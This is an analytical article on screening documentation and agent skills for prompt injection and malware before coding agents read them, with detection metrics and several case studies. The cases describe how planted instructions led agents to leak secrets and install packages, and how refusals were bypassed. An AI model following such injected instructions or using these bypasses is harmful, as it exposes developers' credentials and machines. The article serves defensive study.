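# Screening documentation for malware-related patterns before AI agents read it: signals and false-positive costs

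## How documentation reaches an AI agent and how screening is judged

AI coding agents, such as Claude Code, Cursor and GitHub Copilot, read files, write code and run commands on a developer's machine. Their language models' training data ends at some date, and software libraries keep changing after it, so many developers connect their agents to a documentation service. The service keeps a searchable collection of documentation for many libraries and returns passages in response to an agent's queries. The main example is Context7, which the company Upstash runs. Upstash has said it indexes over 110,000 libraries.

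Much of the documentation an agent reads comes from strangers, and the agent may act on it. Some services therefore screen content before agents can read it. They look for text written to take control of the agent and for malware-related patterns, which are features of text or code that often accompany malicious software, such as a command that downloads a script and runs it. Screening can fail by letting harmful text through or by rejecting good documentation. The second error is a real danger because legitimate technical writing is full of install commands, passwords and shell scripts.

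### From a repository to a command

According to Context7's *Adding Libraries*, anyone can add a public repository to the service by pasting in its address, even if they don't own it. This can bring in, for example, a README (the repository's introductory file) that tells the reader to install a package. Context7 reads the documentation files (Markdown, plain text, notebooks and a few other formats) and skips the source code. If the repository has little or no documentation, it generates examples from the source code instead. It refreshes popular libraries automatically, and a maintainer can set up a refresh on every change to the main branch. The text can therefore change after a scan, and a clean result covers only the text that was scanned.

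Next the service cuts the documentation into chunks, the individual passages or code snippets that it screens, stores and later retrieves. Akar's *Introducing Context7* lists the processing steps: extract the snippets, have a language model add short explanations and metadata, convert the result into numerical vectors for search by meaning, rank the results by relevance, and cache them. The chunk therefore differs slightly from what the maintainer wrote. Some chunks have no original in the documentation. When Context7 answers a question badly, it can have an agent work on a copy of the repository, then store what the agent writes and use it to answer similar questions. About 17% of the snippets it served came from this source, according to Upstash's *How Context7 Researches Its Own Weak Spots* (2026).

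According to Context7's *Prompt Injection and Malware Pattern Detection*, a classifier examines each chunk from public sources before the service indexes it. The service leaves out flagged chunks and adds the rest to the searchable store.

The agent reaches the store through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard by which agents request content and tools from outside servers. Context7's *Tools Reference* describes two calls. The first turns a library's name into an identifier, and the second sends a question about that library and gets passages back. The agent's model writes the question. Josh and Akar report in *Context7 Without Context Bloat* that the service used to return whatever its vector search found, but now ranks the results on its own server and sends only the most relevant passages. This cut the average reply from about 9,700 tokens (words or parts of words) to 3,300. Shorter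 replies save money, but an agent may see an install command without the page that surrounded it. Context7's *API Guide* advises developers to cache replies for hours or days, so a passage could stay in use for some time after the service removes it.

The sample reply in the *Tools Reference* is harmless and answers a question about logging users in to a web application. It contains an `npm install` command for two packages, followed by code that reads a secret from an environment variable. Malware also fetches outside code and reads credentials.

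When the reply arrives, the agent's software adds it to the model's context, the text the model works from. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes the resulting exposure: an MCP response is "data to the protocol but instructions to the LLM". Nothing in the format forces the model to treat the response only as information.

Then the agent runs the command. The *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a software security non-profit, warns that many developers let their agents proceed without confirming each step, and that the agent then acts with the developer's full permissions. The Python command `pip install` can run code from a package during installation, before anyone has used the package. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (Bagmar and Saraf, 2026) points out that the agent's process also inherits the developer's environment, including API keys and cloud credentials.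 Documentation written by a stranger can therefore lead an agent to run a stranger's code in the same environment as those credentials.

### Three kinds of harmful content

A screener may be looking for any of three things, and a detector that is good at one can be useless for another.

Prompt injection is text in fetched content that tries to redirect the agent from its user's task. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) calls it indirect when the attacker plants the instruction in a document, web page or tool output that the model will read later, rather than addressing the model directly. The same paper describes MCP as especially exposed because agents often treat retrieved content as an authoritative part of the task. Crude injections tell the model to ignore its earlier instructions, while subtler ones sound like project advice. In *You Told Me to Do It* (2026), Kao, Li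 and colleagues planted text in real READMEs asking the agent to send a private file elsewhere. They phrased these requests as direct orders, friendly security tips, team habits or company policy. Injected text can also arrive outside the retrieved chunks. Infosecurity Magazine's *ContextCrush Flaw Exposes AI Development Tools to Attacks* reports that Context7 once passed on library maintainers' custom instructions unfiltered.

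Harmful code does its damage by running, so it does not need to persuade the model of anything. *LivePI* (2026), a benchmark of attacks on agents, includes a plausible-looking Python repository with hostile functions hidden among its utility modules. One of them searches the user's files for anything that resembles a cryptocurrency wallet and emails a report. The functions run as soon as a program imports the package. A detector that looks for suspicious instructions to the model will miss this attack because the code contains none.

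The remaining kind is an ordinary command with a harmful target. Bagmar and Saraf study only this kind. Their attacker edits only setup documentation, and each edit breaks one of three conditions for a safe installation: the package comes from a trusted source, its name is the one the developer meant, and its version has no known unpatched vulnerability. The attacker may add an unfamiliar package server, replace the real package name `azure-core` with `azurecore`, or specify an old release with a published vulnerability.

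Agents don't reliably catch these problems themselves, which is much of the reason to screen documentation before they read it. The study tested nine combinations of a model and the software around it, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5. With wrong names of the `azurecore` type, Opus 4.8 avoided the trap in all 60 runs, while Cursor's agent fell for it in 28 of 30. Six of the nine combinations always installed a package from an untrusted server on a throwaway public domain. All nine installed the vulnerable versions in all 270 runs.

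The three kinds can overlap. A README line that tells an agent to copy a private file to a remote machine is an injection, and the copy command is also harmful code. The distinction still matters for screening because the evidence of an injection is in the wording, the evidence of harmful code is in the code, which the chunk may not include, and the evidence of a harmful target is on another server.

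### The same command, safe or hostile

This last case is the central difficulty. An installation command can look exactly the same whether its target is safe or hostile.

In an example from Bagmar and Saraf, a README tells the reader to add a company's internal package server because one package, `httpclient`, exists only there. Many honest companies do this. But the same server also offers `pytest`, a popular testing tool, under the invented version number 99.0.0. The installer compares the versions on the public and internal servers, picks the higher one, and fetches the poisoned copy. Everything in the README could appear in legitimate documentation. A screener also can't treat the extra-server option as a warning sign by itself, because Bagmar and Saraf found it in over 5,500 READMEs on GitHub (a rough count that includes copies of repositories).

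In *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026) describe a scanner that flagged the official installation command for SDKMAN, a tool for managing software development kits, because someone could compromise the server behind it. The same risk applies to most published installation commands. The researchers think the setup command alone is seldom enough to reach a verdict, so someone has to inspect what it installs.

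In one of the few measurements on documentation itself, Kao and colleagues ran existing detectors over installation files with and without a planted instruction. A scanner that blocks executable code flagged 90% of both the harmless and the tampered files, so its verdicts could not distinguish them. Fifteen participants with technical backgrounds also reviewed three READMEs each, and none identified the planted instruction as suspicious, though the researchers had asked them to review for clarity and had not mentioned security.

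The authors conclude from this that malicious and benign setup instructions are semantically indistinguishable. Their own results are less bleak. GPT-4o, now an old model, flagged 90% of the tampered files and none of the harmless ones when given a one-line prompt asking whether the file was safe. Its detection rate fell to 30% when the planted instruction was behind a link. A screener that asks the right question can spot a request to send away a private file, but it has trouble when the harm lies somewhere it does not look.

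### Why most measurements concern skills

Most published error rates are for agent skills, a type of content related to documentation. A skill is a folder containing a file named SKILL.md, which holds a name, a description and instructions for a task. The folder may also contain scripts and reference material. An agent loads the instructions when the task comes up and follows them. People publish and install skills through skill hubs such as ClawHub.

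Researchers study skills because the materials they need are readily available. Yang, Ying and colleagues found six public datasets of skills with security labels. They could run four of the detectors that hubs use because the source code is open, and they could collect scan reports for tens of thousands of skills because ClawHub publishes them. Documentation services provide much less material. Context7's page on its classifier, for example, gives no error rates.

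The figures for skills apply only partly to documentation. Both kinds of text mention shell commands, credentials and installation steps, but a skill is written to command an agent, so imperative sentences are normal in it, whereas reference documentation mostly describes. A skill also states its purpose and arrives whole, so a detector can check whether reading a password fits that purpose. A single chunk of documentation provides little context for that check, but it is also short, so it has fewer chances to trigger a rule. It is hard to say which effect is larger, so a false-positive rate for skills is at best a rough indication of the rate for documentation.

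### Counting the errors

In an invented example used to define the measures, a service screens 1,000 chunks, 10 of which are harmful. The screener flags 9 of the harmful chunks and 20 of the 990 harmless ones.

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| Harmless | 20 | 970 | 990 |
| Total | 29 | 971 | 1,000 |

Suppose a screener checks 1,000 items, 10 of which are harmful, and flags 9 of the harmful items and 20 harmless ones. The base rate is the share of all screened items that are harmful (10 of 1,000, or 1%). Recall is the share of harmful items that the screener flags (9 of 10, or 90%). A false positive is a harmless item that the screener flags, and the false-positive rate is the share of harmless items that it flags (20 of 990, or about 2%). Precision is the share of flagged items that are harmful (9 of 29, or about 31%).

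The last two figures are easy to confuse, and both describe the same 20 mistakes. The 2% matters to a maintainer who wants to know whether the service will drop a harmless page, while an employee who reviews the flagged chunks finds that more than two in three are harmless. Precision also depends on the base rate, so a precision figure from a test set full of attacks can mislead.

F1 combines precision and recall in one number, their harmonic mean:

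F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

The harmonic mean of precision and recall here is 0.46. It stays close to the lower of the two values, so a screener with poor precision scores low even if its recall is high. Plain accuracy would be misleading here, because a screener that never flagged anything would be right about 99% of the chunks, compared with about 97.9% for this one.

F1 does not count the harmless items that the screener correctly leaves alone. A screener that flagged everything would score 0.02 on the invented chunks but 0.75 on the test set of Yang, Ying and colleagues, which has 886 malicious skills and 591 benign ones. An F1 score therefore means little unless the reader knows the share of malicious items in the test set. Yang, Fu and colleagues also report the Matthews correlation coefficient and the area under the precision-recall curve. The Matthews coefficient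 uses all four inner cells of the table and runs from −1 to 1, with 0 for a verdict no better than chance. The invented screener gets 0.52. The area under the precision-recall curve summarizes performance over all possible thresholds instead of one.

The false-positive rate also depends on whether it is measured per chunk, per page or per skill. If a page is split into 20 chunks and each has an independent 2% chance of a false alarm, the page has about a 33% chance of losing at least one chunk. Errors on the same page are probably correlated, which would lower that figure.

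All these numbers depend on someone's decision about what is harmful. Yang, Ying and colleagues reviewed 157 skills that an earlier dataset had labelled malicious and confirmed 95. They sorted the rest by intent and harm, finding 34 benign and setting aside the other 28 as risky or suspicious because the detectors don't make that distinction. Honest documentation that pins a vulnerable version would fall into the risky group, because it harms the reader without the author intending it. Whether flagging it counts as a false positive depends on what the screening service is meant to stop.

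## Recorded cases of harmful documentation

Security researchers have published several cases in which documentation or a similar instruction file led a coding agent to do harm, or could have. Five are described in enough detail to judge what a screener could have noticed in the text. Attackers carried out some of them, and researchers staged the others. A staged attack is good evidence that a method works, but poor evidence of how often criminals use it.

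### Context7's unfiltered rules

Of the five cases, only ContextCrush directly concerns a documentation service, Context7. Whoever registers a library on Context7 can add "Custom Rules", instructions meant to help agents understand the documentation. Researchers at the security company Noma found that the service delivered these rules to agents exactly as written. According to Infosecurity Magazine, an attacker could register a new library with a GitHub account, put hostile instructions in the rules, and wait for a developer's agent to look up the library.

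In a demonstration by Noma, a poisoned library entry contained rules instructing the agent to find `.env` files, where developers often keep passwords and API keys, and send their contents to a repository under the attacker's control. The agent was then supposed to delete local files under the pretext of tidying up. It received these instructions alongside legitimate documentation, in reply to an ordinary question. An attacker would still have to get developers to choose the poisoned library, but Noma pointed out that people can manipulate GitHub reputation, popularity rankings and trust scores.

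Noma reported the flaw to Upstash on 18 February 2026. Upstash started work the next day and on 23 February deployed a fix that sanitizes the rules and adds other safeguards. Noma made the flaw public on 5 March. Infosecurity Magazine reports no evidence that anyone used it in a real attack.

The flaw received an entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities in August. The magazine called it critical, but NVD's *CVE-2026-75130 Detail* (2026), a page of the US government's vulnerability database, shows a score of 6.4 out of 10, or "medium". That score comes from the security company VulnCheck, and NVD has not added its own. VulnCheck rated the attack as easy to carry out over the network, requiring only a basic account and a routine action by the victim. It rated the damage to Context7 itself at zero and the damage to connected systems at the highest level for confidentiality,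 integrity and availability. The scoring formula gives less weight to damage to connected systems, which probably explains much of the difference between "critical" and "medium".

VulnCheck's *Context7 2.1.2 Prompt Injection via Custom AI Instructions* classifies the weakness as a failure to neutralize input that ends up in a language model's prompt. A screener could have flagged that input, because instructions to send away the contents of a secrets file or delete a user's work don't belong in a guide to using a library. Screening only the documentation chunks would have missed it, so a service has to screen every field that a stranger can write and an agent will read.

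### Official documentation that names missing packages

Many websites now publish a file named `llms.txt`, which summarizes the site so that AI agents needn't read every page. Common Crawl's *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026) explains that Jeremy Howard proposed the format in September 2024, with a title, a one-paragraph summary and annotated links. Common Crawl, which archives web pages, analysed 584,107 of these files and found prompt injections in a few. The security company Pandex found a different problem, which can occur even if no attacker has changed the text.

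Pandex checked the packages and web domains that such files mention. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* gives 8,565 files and 237 references to software that no longer existed, did not exist yet, had moved, or had a misspelled name. Other reports, based on an Ars Technica article about what is evidently the same study, give slightly different numbers. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* gives 8,265 files on 6,214 domains, and Xakep's *Ошибки в llms.txt вынуждают Claude, Codex и Hermes запускать чужой код* (2026) gives 227 instructions on 120 sites. Each pair of totals differs by a single digit, so someone may have miscopied them. By TechRadar's figures, about 2% of the domains had the problem. The affected domains belonged to defence contractors, large technology firms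 and Fortune 500 companies.

If a vendor's documentation names an unregistered package, anyone can register that name, and the documentation will then direct readers to whatever the new owner has put there. The same can happen with an expired domain in a command that downloads and runs a script. Pandex found unclaimed names on six package registries, including PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript, and abandoned addresses at several web hosting companies.

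The researchers registered some of these names and uploaded harmless packages that contacted a Pandex server when they ran. Tom's Hardware reports that the first contact came after four minutes. Xakep reports that a contact came from a Fortune 500 company's network in less than an hour, which may be a later one, and that a few dozen more followed from other companies and startups. The researchers traced what had started the installations and identified Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes agent.

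Pandex also tested individual models by asking each agent to build and run a small project from a vendor's documentation, without mentioning `llms.txt` or planting any injection. According to Tom's Hardware, the models it calls GPT-5 Luna and Sol ran the planted package at least 90% of the time, compared with 30% for Claude Opus 4.8 at medium effort. Opus 4.8 had avoided every misspelled package in Bagmar and Saraf's 60 runs. It may have recognized those misspellings because they resembled the names of well-known packages, whereas a vendor's own obscure package has no familiar counterpart.

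Xakep reports that the `llms.txt` file of Clerk, which provides user login systems, contained an `npx` command for a package that did not originally exist on npm. Before the researchers found the command, an unknown person had registered the name and uploaded malware. The `npx` tool runs a program from a package and downloads the package if the machine doesn't already have it. Clerk explained that one of its own packages contained a program with the same name, so an agent that ran that copy was safe. An agent on a machine without that copy could have downloaded the malware. Clerk has since corrected the file, and Mondo's *Popularni AI agenti uhvaćeni u opasnom propustu* notes that nobody knows whether it led to any infections.

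Mistakes like these can go uncorrected for a long time because people rarely see the file, which doesn't appear in the browser, and the person who writes the documentation may not be the one who names the package. Tom's Hardware also cites an analysis of 13 million packages in which about 30% to 60%, depending on the programming ecosystem, lost development activity within two years of release.

Language models also introduce errors into documentation. Aikido's *Agent Skills Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* describes a nonexistent npm package whose name a model had invented. The name spread to 237 GitHub repositories (the match with Pandex's number is a coincidence) because people copied, adapted and translated the skill files containing it without checking. A researcher registered the name before anyone else did, using an empty package, and soon saw downloads.

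Reading the text would not have exposed any of these names, because the command was ordinary and, in the Pandex cases, appeared on the vendor's official site. According to Xakep, security software on the developer's machine has the same difficulty, since it detects only a trusted agent installing something from a trusted registry. A registry lookup, however, would reveal a name that nobody has claimed.

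### A repository that passes review

Mozilla's security researchers at 0DIN built a repository in which the harmful part of the attack was not in any file. In *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine*, a developer downloads this attacker-controlled repository and asks Claude Code to get it running.

The attack depends on an error the attacker planned. SecurityWeek explains that the setup notes require a Python package that stops with an error if anyone uses it before initializing it. The error message gives the command to fix the problem. Claude Code runs the command, as many developers would, which starts a shell script.

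According to Tom's Hardware's *AI coding agents can be tricked into installing malware*, the script next reads a text record from the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of domain names, instead of downloading a file from a web address, which a scanner could check. DNS text records have many legitimate uses, including email configuration, but this one contains an encoded command that opens a reverse shell, a connection through which the attacker can run commands on the developer's machine with the developer's permissions.

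0DIN staged this case, so it is a demonstration rather than a known attack. The attacker can change the DNS record at any time without touching the repository, so a scanner could follow every step, find a harmless record and pass the repository an hour before the attacker replaces the record.

A documentation screener would have found setup notes that named an ordinary package. The crucial suggestion came from an error message, which appears only when the software runs and may never be in the documentation. A tool that reads code might flag a script that executes the answer to a DNS query, but 0DIN judged that each file looks unremarkable and passes review. Context7 would probably never examine the script, because it skips source code if a library has enough documentation.

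### An instruction file in the Downloads folder

The remaining two cases involve files meant to instruct an agent, so they are closer to skills than to reference documentation. One is an `AGENTS.md` file, a plain text file that developers put in a project folder to tell coding agents how to work there. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* reports that the company Forever Security stopped a customer's agent from installing a malicious npm package, `function-color`. The company's researchers traced the instruction to an `AGENTS.md` file in the customer's Downloads folder. Mynavi News' *CodexとClaude Codeに攻撃の恐れ、悪意ある指示ファイルで不正コード実行* (2026) dates the researchers' report to 22 October 2026.

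The researchers never established how the file got there, but according to TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware*, they assume a browser saved it from a compromised website. Websites can put a file in that folder without the user clicking anything, and Clubic's *Codex et Claude Code peuvent être piégés par un fichier* reports that the news site BleepingComputer checked a harmless demonstration of this. Operating systems ask for approval before running a downloaded program, but they have no such check for text.

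The file was 13 kilobytes long and looked like engineering guidelines. Its length and dull tone helped it get past Codex, which refuses a short request to install the package. In more than 90% of attempts, when Forever's researchers opened Codex in the folder and gave it any task, it first added a server to its own settings and then installed the package. In most attempts the researchers used a harmless substitute that opened a calculator, and they ran the real package once in an isolated virtual machine. The changed settings applied to the whole computer, so later Codex sessions ran the attacker's command in every project.

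Codex follows such a file only in a folder it trusts, and the Downloads folder counts as trusted once the user has worked there. About half of Forever's customers start an agent in that folder at least sometimes, and Clubic reports that Claude Code had started there more than 1,300 times on their machines.

The researchers wrote a new file for Claude Code because the real one targeted Codex and Claude was much harder to fool. Their file presented a settings change as a way to connect to the company's internal gateway. The change actually sent the agent's traffic, including the user's login token, to the researchers' server. Claude followed through about half the time, and the researchers could then use the stolen token to take over the account. They also ran code within the same session in about a fifth of tests. The 90% rate for Codex and the 50% rate for Claude come from different attacks,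 so they don't measure the relative safety of the two products. Both figures also come from a company whose business is protecting agents.

The customer's file contained visible warning signs. One was the package name, but a list of known malware would not have caught it for most of the package's life, because the campaign behind it went unnoticed for about two years. The instruction to change the agent's settings is a better sign, but it can also be legitimate, since installation guides for MCP servers routinely ask for the same kind of change and many companies do have an internal gateway. Splitting the file into chunks might have helped by separating the instruction from much of the padding, though chunking usually loses context.

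### ClawHavoc's false prerequisites

The largest recorded campaign used skills on ClawHub, which serves users of OpenClaw, an AI assistant that people run on their own machines. The Hacker News' *Researchers Find 341 Malicious ClawHub* (2026) reports that Koi Security audited 2,857 skills there and judged 341 malicious. Of these, 335 belonged to this campaign, which Koi named ClawHavoc.

These skills had believable names that suggested cryptocurrency trackers or video summarizers. The attack was in the installation guide's list of prerequisites. On Apple computers, the supposed prerequisite led to Atomic Stealer, a program that steals data. Windows users had to download a password-protected ZIP file from GitHub and run the program inside it, according to SC Media. The password prevents many automatic scanners from opening the archive, and it doesn't make the download look worse to a person.

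The 16 February update to Koi Security's *ClawHavoc 341 Malicious ClawedBot Skills Found by the Bot They Were Targeting* (2026) reported that the number of malicious skills had grown to 824, out of more than 10,700. Some of the new ones posed as security scanners. The malicious share had fallen from about 12% to just under 8% because the hub had grown even faster. Palo Alto Networks' Unit 42 cites a higher estimate from Bitdefender, which found malicious payloads in about 17% of the skills it analysed from the platform's first weeks. These percentages are hard to compare because the companies examined different samples, and they don't show how many users were harmed.

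Unlike the staged cases, this was live malware on a public site. The text told the user to download a program from elsewhere and run it. Plenty of legitimate software also has prerequisites, and some requires a separate installer. But a password-protected archive is much less common, and a skill that summarizes videos should rarely need an unknown Windows program. A screener can spot both clues without downloading anything.

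### The cases by visible signal

The table sorts the cases by what a screener could have found in the text alone.

| Visible signal | Case | Type of text | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Suspicious command | ClawHavoc | Skills | Live malware on a public hub |
| Plain-language request | ContextCrush | Library owner's rules in a documentation service | Demonstration |
| Plain-language request | Downloads folder | Agent instruction file | Live attack, stopped before installation |
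| Nothing suspicious | Stale `llms.txt` files | Official documentation | Real installations of harmless test packages; malware behind one name |
| Nothing suspicious | 0DIN repository | Setup notes | Demonstration |

Some of these placements are debatable. The `AGENTS.md` file also led to an installation command, but that command would look normal in any JavaScript project, and the request to change the agent's settings was more revealing. ClawHavoc's prerequisites were partly ordinary sentences addressed to a person, but they are in the top row because a fixed rule can describe the action involved, downloading and running a program. Fixed rules do worse on requests like those in ContextCrush because an attacker can reword them freely.

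Help Net Security's *Hidden instructions in README files can make AI agents leak data* reports tests in which plain-language requests in documentation led agents to send private data to an outside server in up to 85% of cases.

Figures from the security company Ox Security suggest that such requests are also common in malicious skills. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path* reports that Ox analysed 542,207 open-source components between July and October 2026. Among the skills that Ox flagged, 26% contained prompt injection or a related attack in which a tool's description misleads the agent, and 44% contained instructions to send data out. None ran code during installation or loading. Among flagged MCP servers, 22% contained injection or misleading descriptions, and 16% had code that ran during installation or loading. These percentages cover only what Ox's methods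 caught, so an attack like 0DIN's, with nothing suspicious in its files, could easily be missing.

Five cases can't show how common each signal is, partly because researchers tend to publish new or surprising attacks. How common a signal appears also depends on whether we count cases or files. ClawHavoc is one of the five cases but accounts for hundreds of malicious files, while the Downloads attack involved a single file on one customer's machine. A screener that looked only for suspicious commands could have caught a large share of the malicious files, but it would probably have missed ContextCrush, the stale package names and the 0DIN repository, the three cases closest to the documentation that agents look up.

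## Where screening takes place

Screening can take place before a service stores a passage of documentation, when the service delivers it to an agent, or when someone installs what the passage recommends. Similarly, a hub can scan skills at publication, and a company or developer can scan them again before installing them. The stage determines what evidence a detector has, how long it can take, and how many people a mistake affects.

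### Before indexing

A service that screens before indexing has access to the source and its owner's record, but it doesn't know who will ask for a passage, what they will ask, or what their agents can do. In *Scanning AI Agent Skills*, JFrog, which sells tools for storing and checking software packages, calls behaviour "suspicious" if it could be harmful or innocent depending on context the scanner lacks. *Runtime Skill Audit* (2026) points out that some attacks take effect only when the agent interprets the text during a task, so inspecting the files alone may not reveal them.

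Screening at this stage can take longer because no user is waiting. In a study by Yang and colleagues, detectors using only static rules averaged 0.05 to 25 seconds per skill, while those using a language model averaged 20 to 271 seconds. There is also time for human review. *SkillScreen* (2026) describes a detector that scores a skill's text before use and sends high-scoring skills to a human reviewer.

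Money may be a tighter limit. The language-model detectors cost between $0.0004 and $0.55 per skill. Upstash's *Inside Context7's Quality Stack* (2025) shows an entry for Next.js, a web framework, with 9,372 code snippets. Screening that many items would cost about $4 at the lowest price and $5,200 at the highest. Snippets are usually much shorter than skills, so the real cost would be lower, but a service with over 100,000 libraries probably can't afford to run the most expensive detectors on every snippet.

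A mistake at this stage affects everyone who uses the library. If the screener misses a harmful chunk, any agent that looks up the library may receive it. If it rejects a good page about configuring credentials, agents can't retrieve that page and may fall back on outdated training data. The developer is unlikely to notice, because the reply doesn't show that anything is missing.

### On delivery to the agent

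A screener that runs at delivery can examine the whole reply, including text that never went through indexing, such as the hostile rules in ContextCrush. This is also the only stage where the user's question is available to a screener. A passage about reading cloud credentials is normal in an answer about deploying an application but strange in one about sorting a table.

How much of the user's question a screener can access depends on where it runs. Context7's *data privacy* explains that the service receives the agent's query but not the user's prompt, and that the agent has instructions to leave passwords, personal data and proprietary code out of the query. A screener on the developer's own machine could use the whole conversation. Context7 already sends the query to language models that choose the most relevant documentation. It could in principle add a safety check to that step, but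 it describes the step only as ranking.

Knowing the question may help less than expected, because the search has already selected passages that match it, and an attacker can include one harmful step in an otherwise useful answer about deployment.

There is also less time, because the developer is waiting and the agent may look up several things during one task. Even a 20-second delay per lookup would be noticeable, although a short reply should take less time to check than a whole skill. Reusing the results of earlier checks can save time. Trail of Bits' *We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025) introduces a wrapper for MCP connections that can scan a server's instructions and tool descriptions for prompt injection. The wrapper also records the version the user first trusted, so that it can detect later changes. This works well for text that rarely changes, but documentation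 replies vary with the question.

If a developer runs their own screener, a false alarm removes one passage from the reply that developer receives, and the rest may be enough. If the service runs the same detector for everyone, a popular passage that triggers it will disappear from many replies, which has much the same effect as rejecting it before indexing.

### At installation

At installation, a screener can examine the package or skill itself, not just the command that names it, and consider what is already on the machine. *Scan Before You Install* (2026) explains that most scanners examine skills one at a time, although an agent can pass content from one skill to another. An attacker who controls something the agent reads may get the agent to read a private file with one skill and send the file away with another, without modifying either skill. A hub that scans each skill separately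 would miss that combination.

An installation scanner can't check documentation that the agent hasn't fetched yet. Snyk's *Security Audit* (2026), published on the hub skills.sh, gives a medium-risk warning to a skill that queries Context7, because the skill brings text written by outsiders into the model's context. ClawHub's *Context7 Documentation Skill* assesses a different skill with the same purpose and reports no hidden or destructive behaviour. Both assessments are reasonable, since Snyk was warning about the exposure and ClawHub was judging the skill's own behaviour. However, users can't learn from either result whether a particular passage from Context7 is safe.

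Users will usually accept a short wait before installing something. Anthropic's *Get started with skill and plugin scanning* describes a check for corporate customers in which Claude reviews uploaded or edited skills, usually within one to two minutes. According to Anthropic's *Skills for enterprise*, nobody can use a skill until its scan finishes, but skills uploaded through the API are not scanned. A simpler check can be much faster. *Skills are the new npm install, so we scanned ours* (Alfred and Bob, 2026) describes a small company's gate that runs static rules on each new skill in about 3.5 seconds.

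An error here affects one person or organization, and a wrongly blocked user at least knows about it. Anthropic's scan shows the reason for a block, and an authorized administrator can allow the blocked version. Otherwise, the uploader has to change the skill, because uploading the same files again gives the same result.

The scan also has to come before the agent reads the skill, because an agent that opens a suspicious skill to judge it is already exposed to any injection inside. *Distributing Security Controls Through Harness Engineering* (2026) therefore proposes passing the skill to an outside scanner first, so that not even its README reaches the model.

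### Commands that run before the model reads the skill

Some defences depend on the agent's own model recognizing an attack and refusing to take part. Datadog Security Labs' *Malicious Coding Agent Skills and the Risk of Dynamic Context* (2026) shows how the model's recognition and refusal can come too late.

The researchers started with Clawsights, a real skill that claims to rank Claude Code users on a leaderboard. It takes the user's GitHub login token and uploads it to the Clawsights website. They replaced the destination with their own domain and ran the skill in Claude Code with Opus 4.6, which recognized the theft and refused.

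They then moved the theft into a feature called dynamic context. A Claude Code skill can contain shell commands marked with an exclamation mark, for example to insert the latest changes to a project. Claude Code runs these commands and replaces them with their output before giving the text to the model. The token was therefore stolen before Opus read the skill and said it would not execute it.

The model's refusal wasn't dependable. In later tests with Opus 4.7, Claude Code consistently ran the skill without identifying the theft, although Datadog Security Labs cautions against drawing general conclusions about the model from this.

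Organizations can turn off these commands for most skills with the setting `disableSkillShellExecution`. Scanning the skill file before loading could also find them. A skill can arrive in a repository's `.claude/skills/` folder and load once the developer has marked the project as trusted, so scanning at the hub isn't enough. Checks that start when the agent uses a tool can also come too late. jedi.be's *intercepting prompt injection at the syscall level* notes that Claude reads some instruction files before such checks run, and demonstrates a scanner that intercepts the file as the agent opens it.

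Dynamic context is a feature of skills. A command in a documentation passage normally reaches the model as text, so the model has a chance to refuse it.

### What Context7 has published

Upstash has described Context7's screening several times, and the descriptions differ. In December 2025, it reported that its own detection model scanned each snippet for prompt injection before storage and blocked those it flagged with high confidence. More descriptions appeared during 2026 in Context7's *Security*, a blog post by Shannon, *Quality and Safety in Context7*, another by Akar, *Context7 is Ready for Enterprise*, and Context7's *Prompt Injection Detection*, which apparently became the current page on injection and malware patterns. Except for the first, the dates in the table are those of surviving copies, so the changes may have come earlier.

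| Date in 2026 | Text | Method | Target | Sources named |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| February (last update) | Context7, security page | Two independent classifiers in sequence | Prompt injection | Public and private repositories |
| 26 February | Shannon | Two passes before storage | Prompt injection | Submitted repositories and websites |
| 29 April | Akar | Language-model classifier in two layers | Injection and malicious snippets | Not specified |
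| 1 May | Context7, detection page | A classifier and a filter in sequence | Injection; malware patterns "coming soon" | Public and private repositories |
| 11 June | Context7, detection page | A classifier, with additional checks on suspicious content | Injection and malware-related patterns | Public and private sources |
| 26 November | Context7, detection page | A classifier on each chunk before indexing | Injection and malware-related patterns | Public sources |

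The account of malware detection isn't quite consistent. Akar claimed in the post that the service already discarded malicious snippets, but a copy of the detection page from two days later listed malware detection as a future feature. The page may have been out of date, or Akar may have meant something narrower by "malicious snippets".

The November text, unlike the June one, specifies what happens to flagged content. It no longer mentions a second check or the separate process for skills that earlier versions described. Upstash may have simplified the system or only its description.

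None of these accounts specifies which signals the classifier uses, what score leads to a block, how much legitimate documentation it rejects, or how many attacks it misses. Shannon writes that the two-pass design minimizes false positives, but gives no figure. Outsiders can't inspect the method either, because Context7 publishes the code for its MCP server but keeps the parsing and crawling engines private. A researcher could submit a test repository and look for missing snippets, but a missing snippet would not prove that the classifier had flagged it, because the service also removes near-duplicates and older versions of documentation.

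Context7 provides a "Report" button for harmful content that gets through, and warns that it can't guarantee the security of all library documentation. By December 2025, Upstash had updated or disabled hundreds of repositories in response to user reports. Upstash has published no comparable procedure for maintainers whose pages the classifier wrongly rejects. Context7 lists GitHub issues, a Discord community and customer support for general security questions.

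### Public and private sources

Paying customers can connect private repositories to Context7, which also accepts internal sources such as Confluence pages and uploaded files. The November text mentions only public sources, and Upstash doesn't explain the change. This omission doesn't prove that private content goes unscreened.

Employees usually write private documentation, so any such service should encounter harmful text less often and have lower precision. If only one chunk in 10,000 were harmful, fewer than one in 200 chunks flagged by the hypothetical screener described earlier (90% recall, 2% false-positive rate) would be harmful. Internal documentation may also trigger more false alarms than public documentation, since it often tells employees to use the company's own package server or explains where to find its credentials.

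Screening can also expose confidential text. An automatic classifier adds little exposure if the service already processes the text, but a person reviewing flagged passages would see private material. Anthropic limits exposure in its own scanning by deleting the scanned copy and keeping only the result and basic metadata. It does no scanning for organizations that manage their own encryption keys, forbid data retention, or use its configuration for HIPAA, the US health privacy law. Anthropic gives no reason for these exceptions, though all three arrangements restrict how a provider handles customer data.

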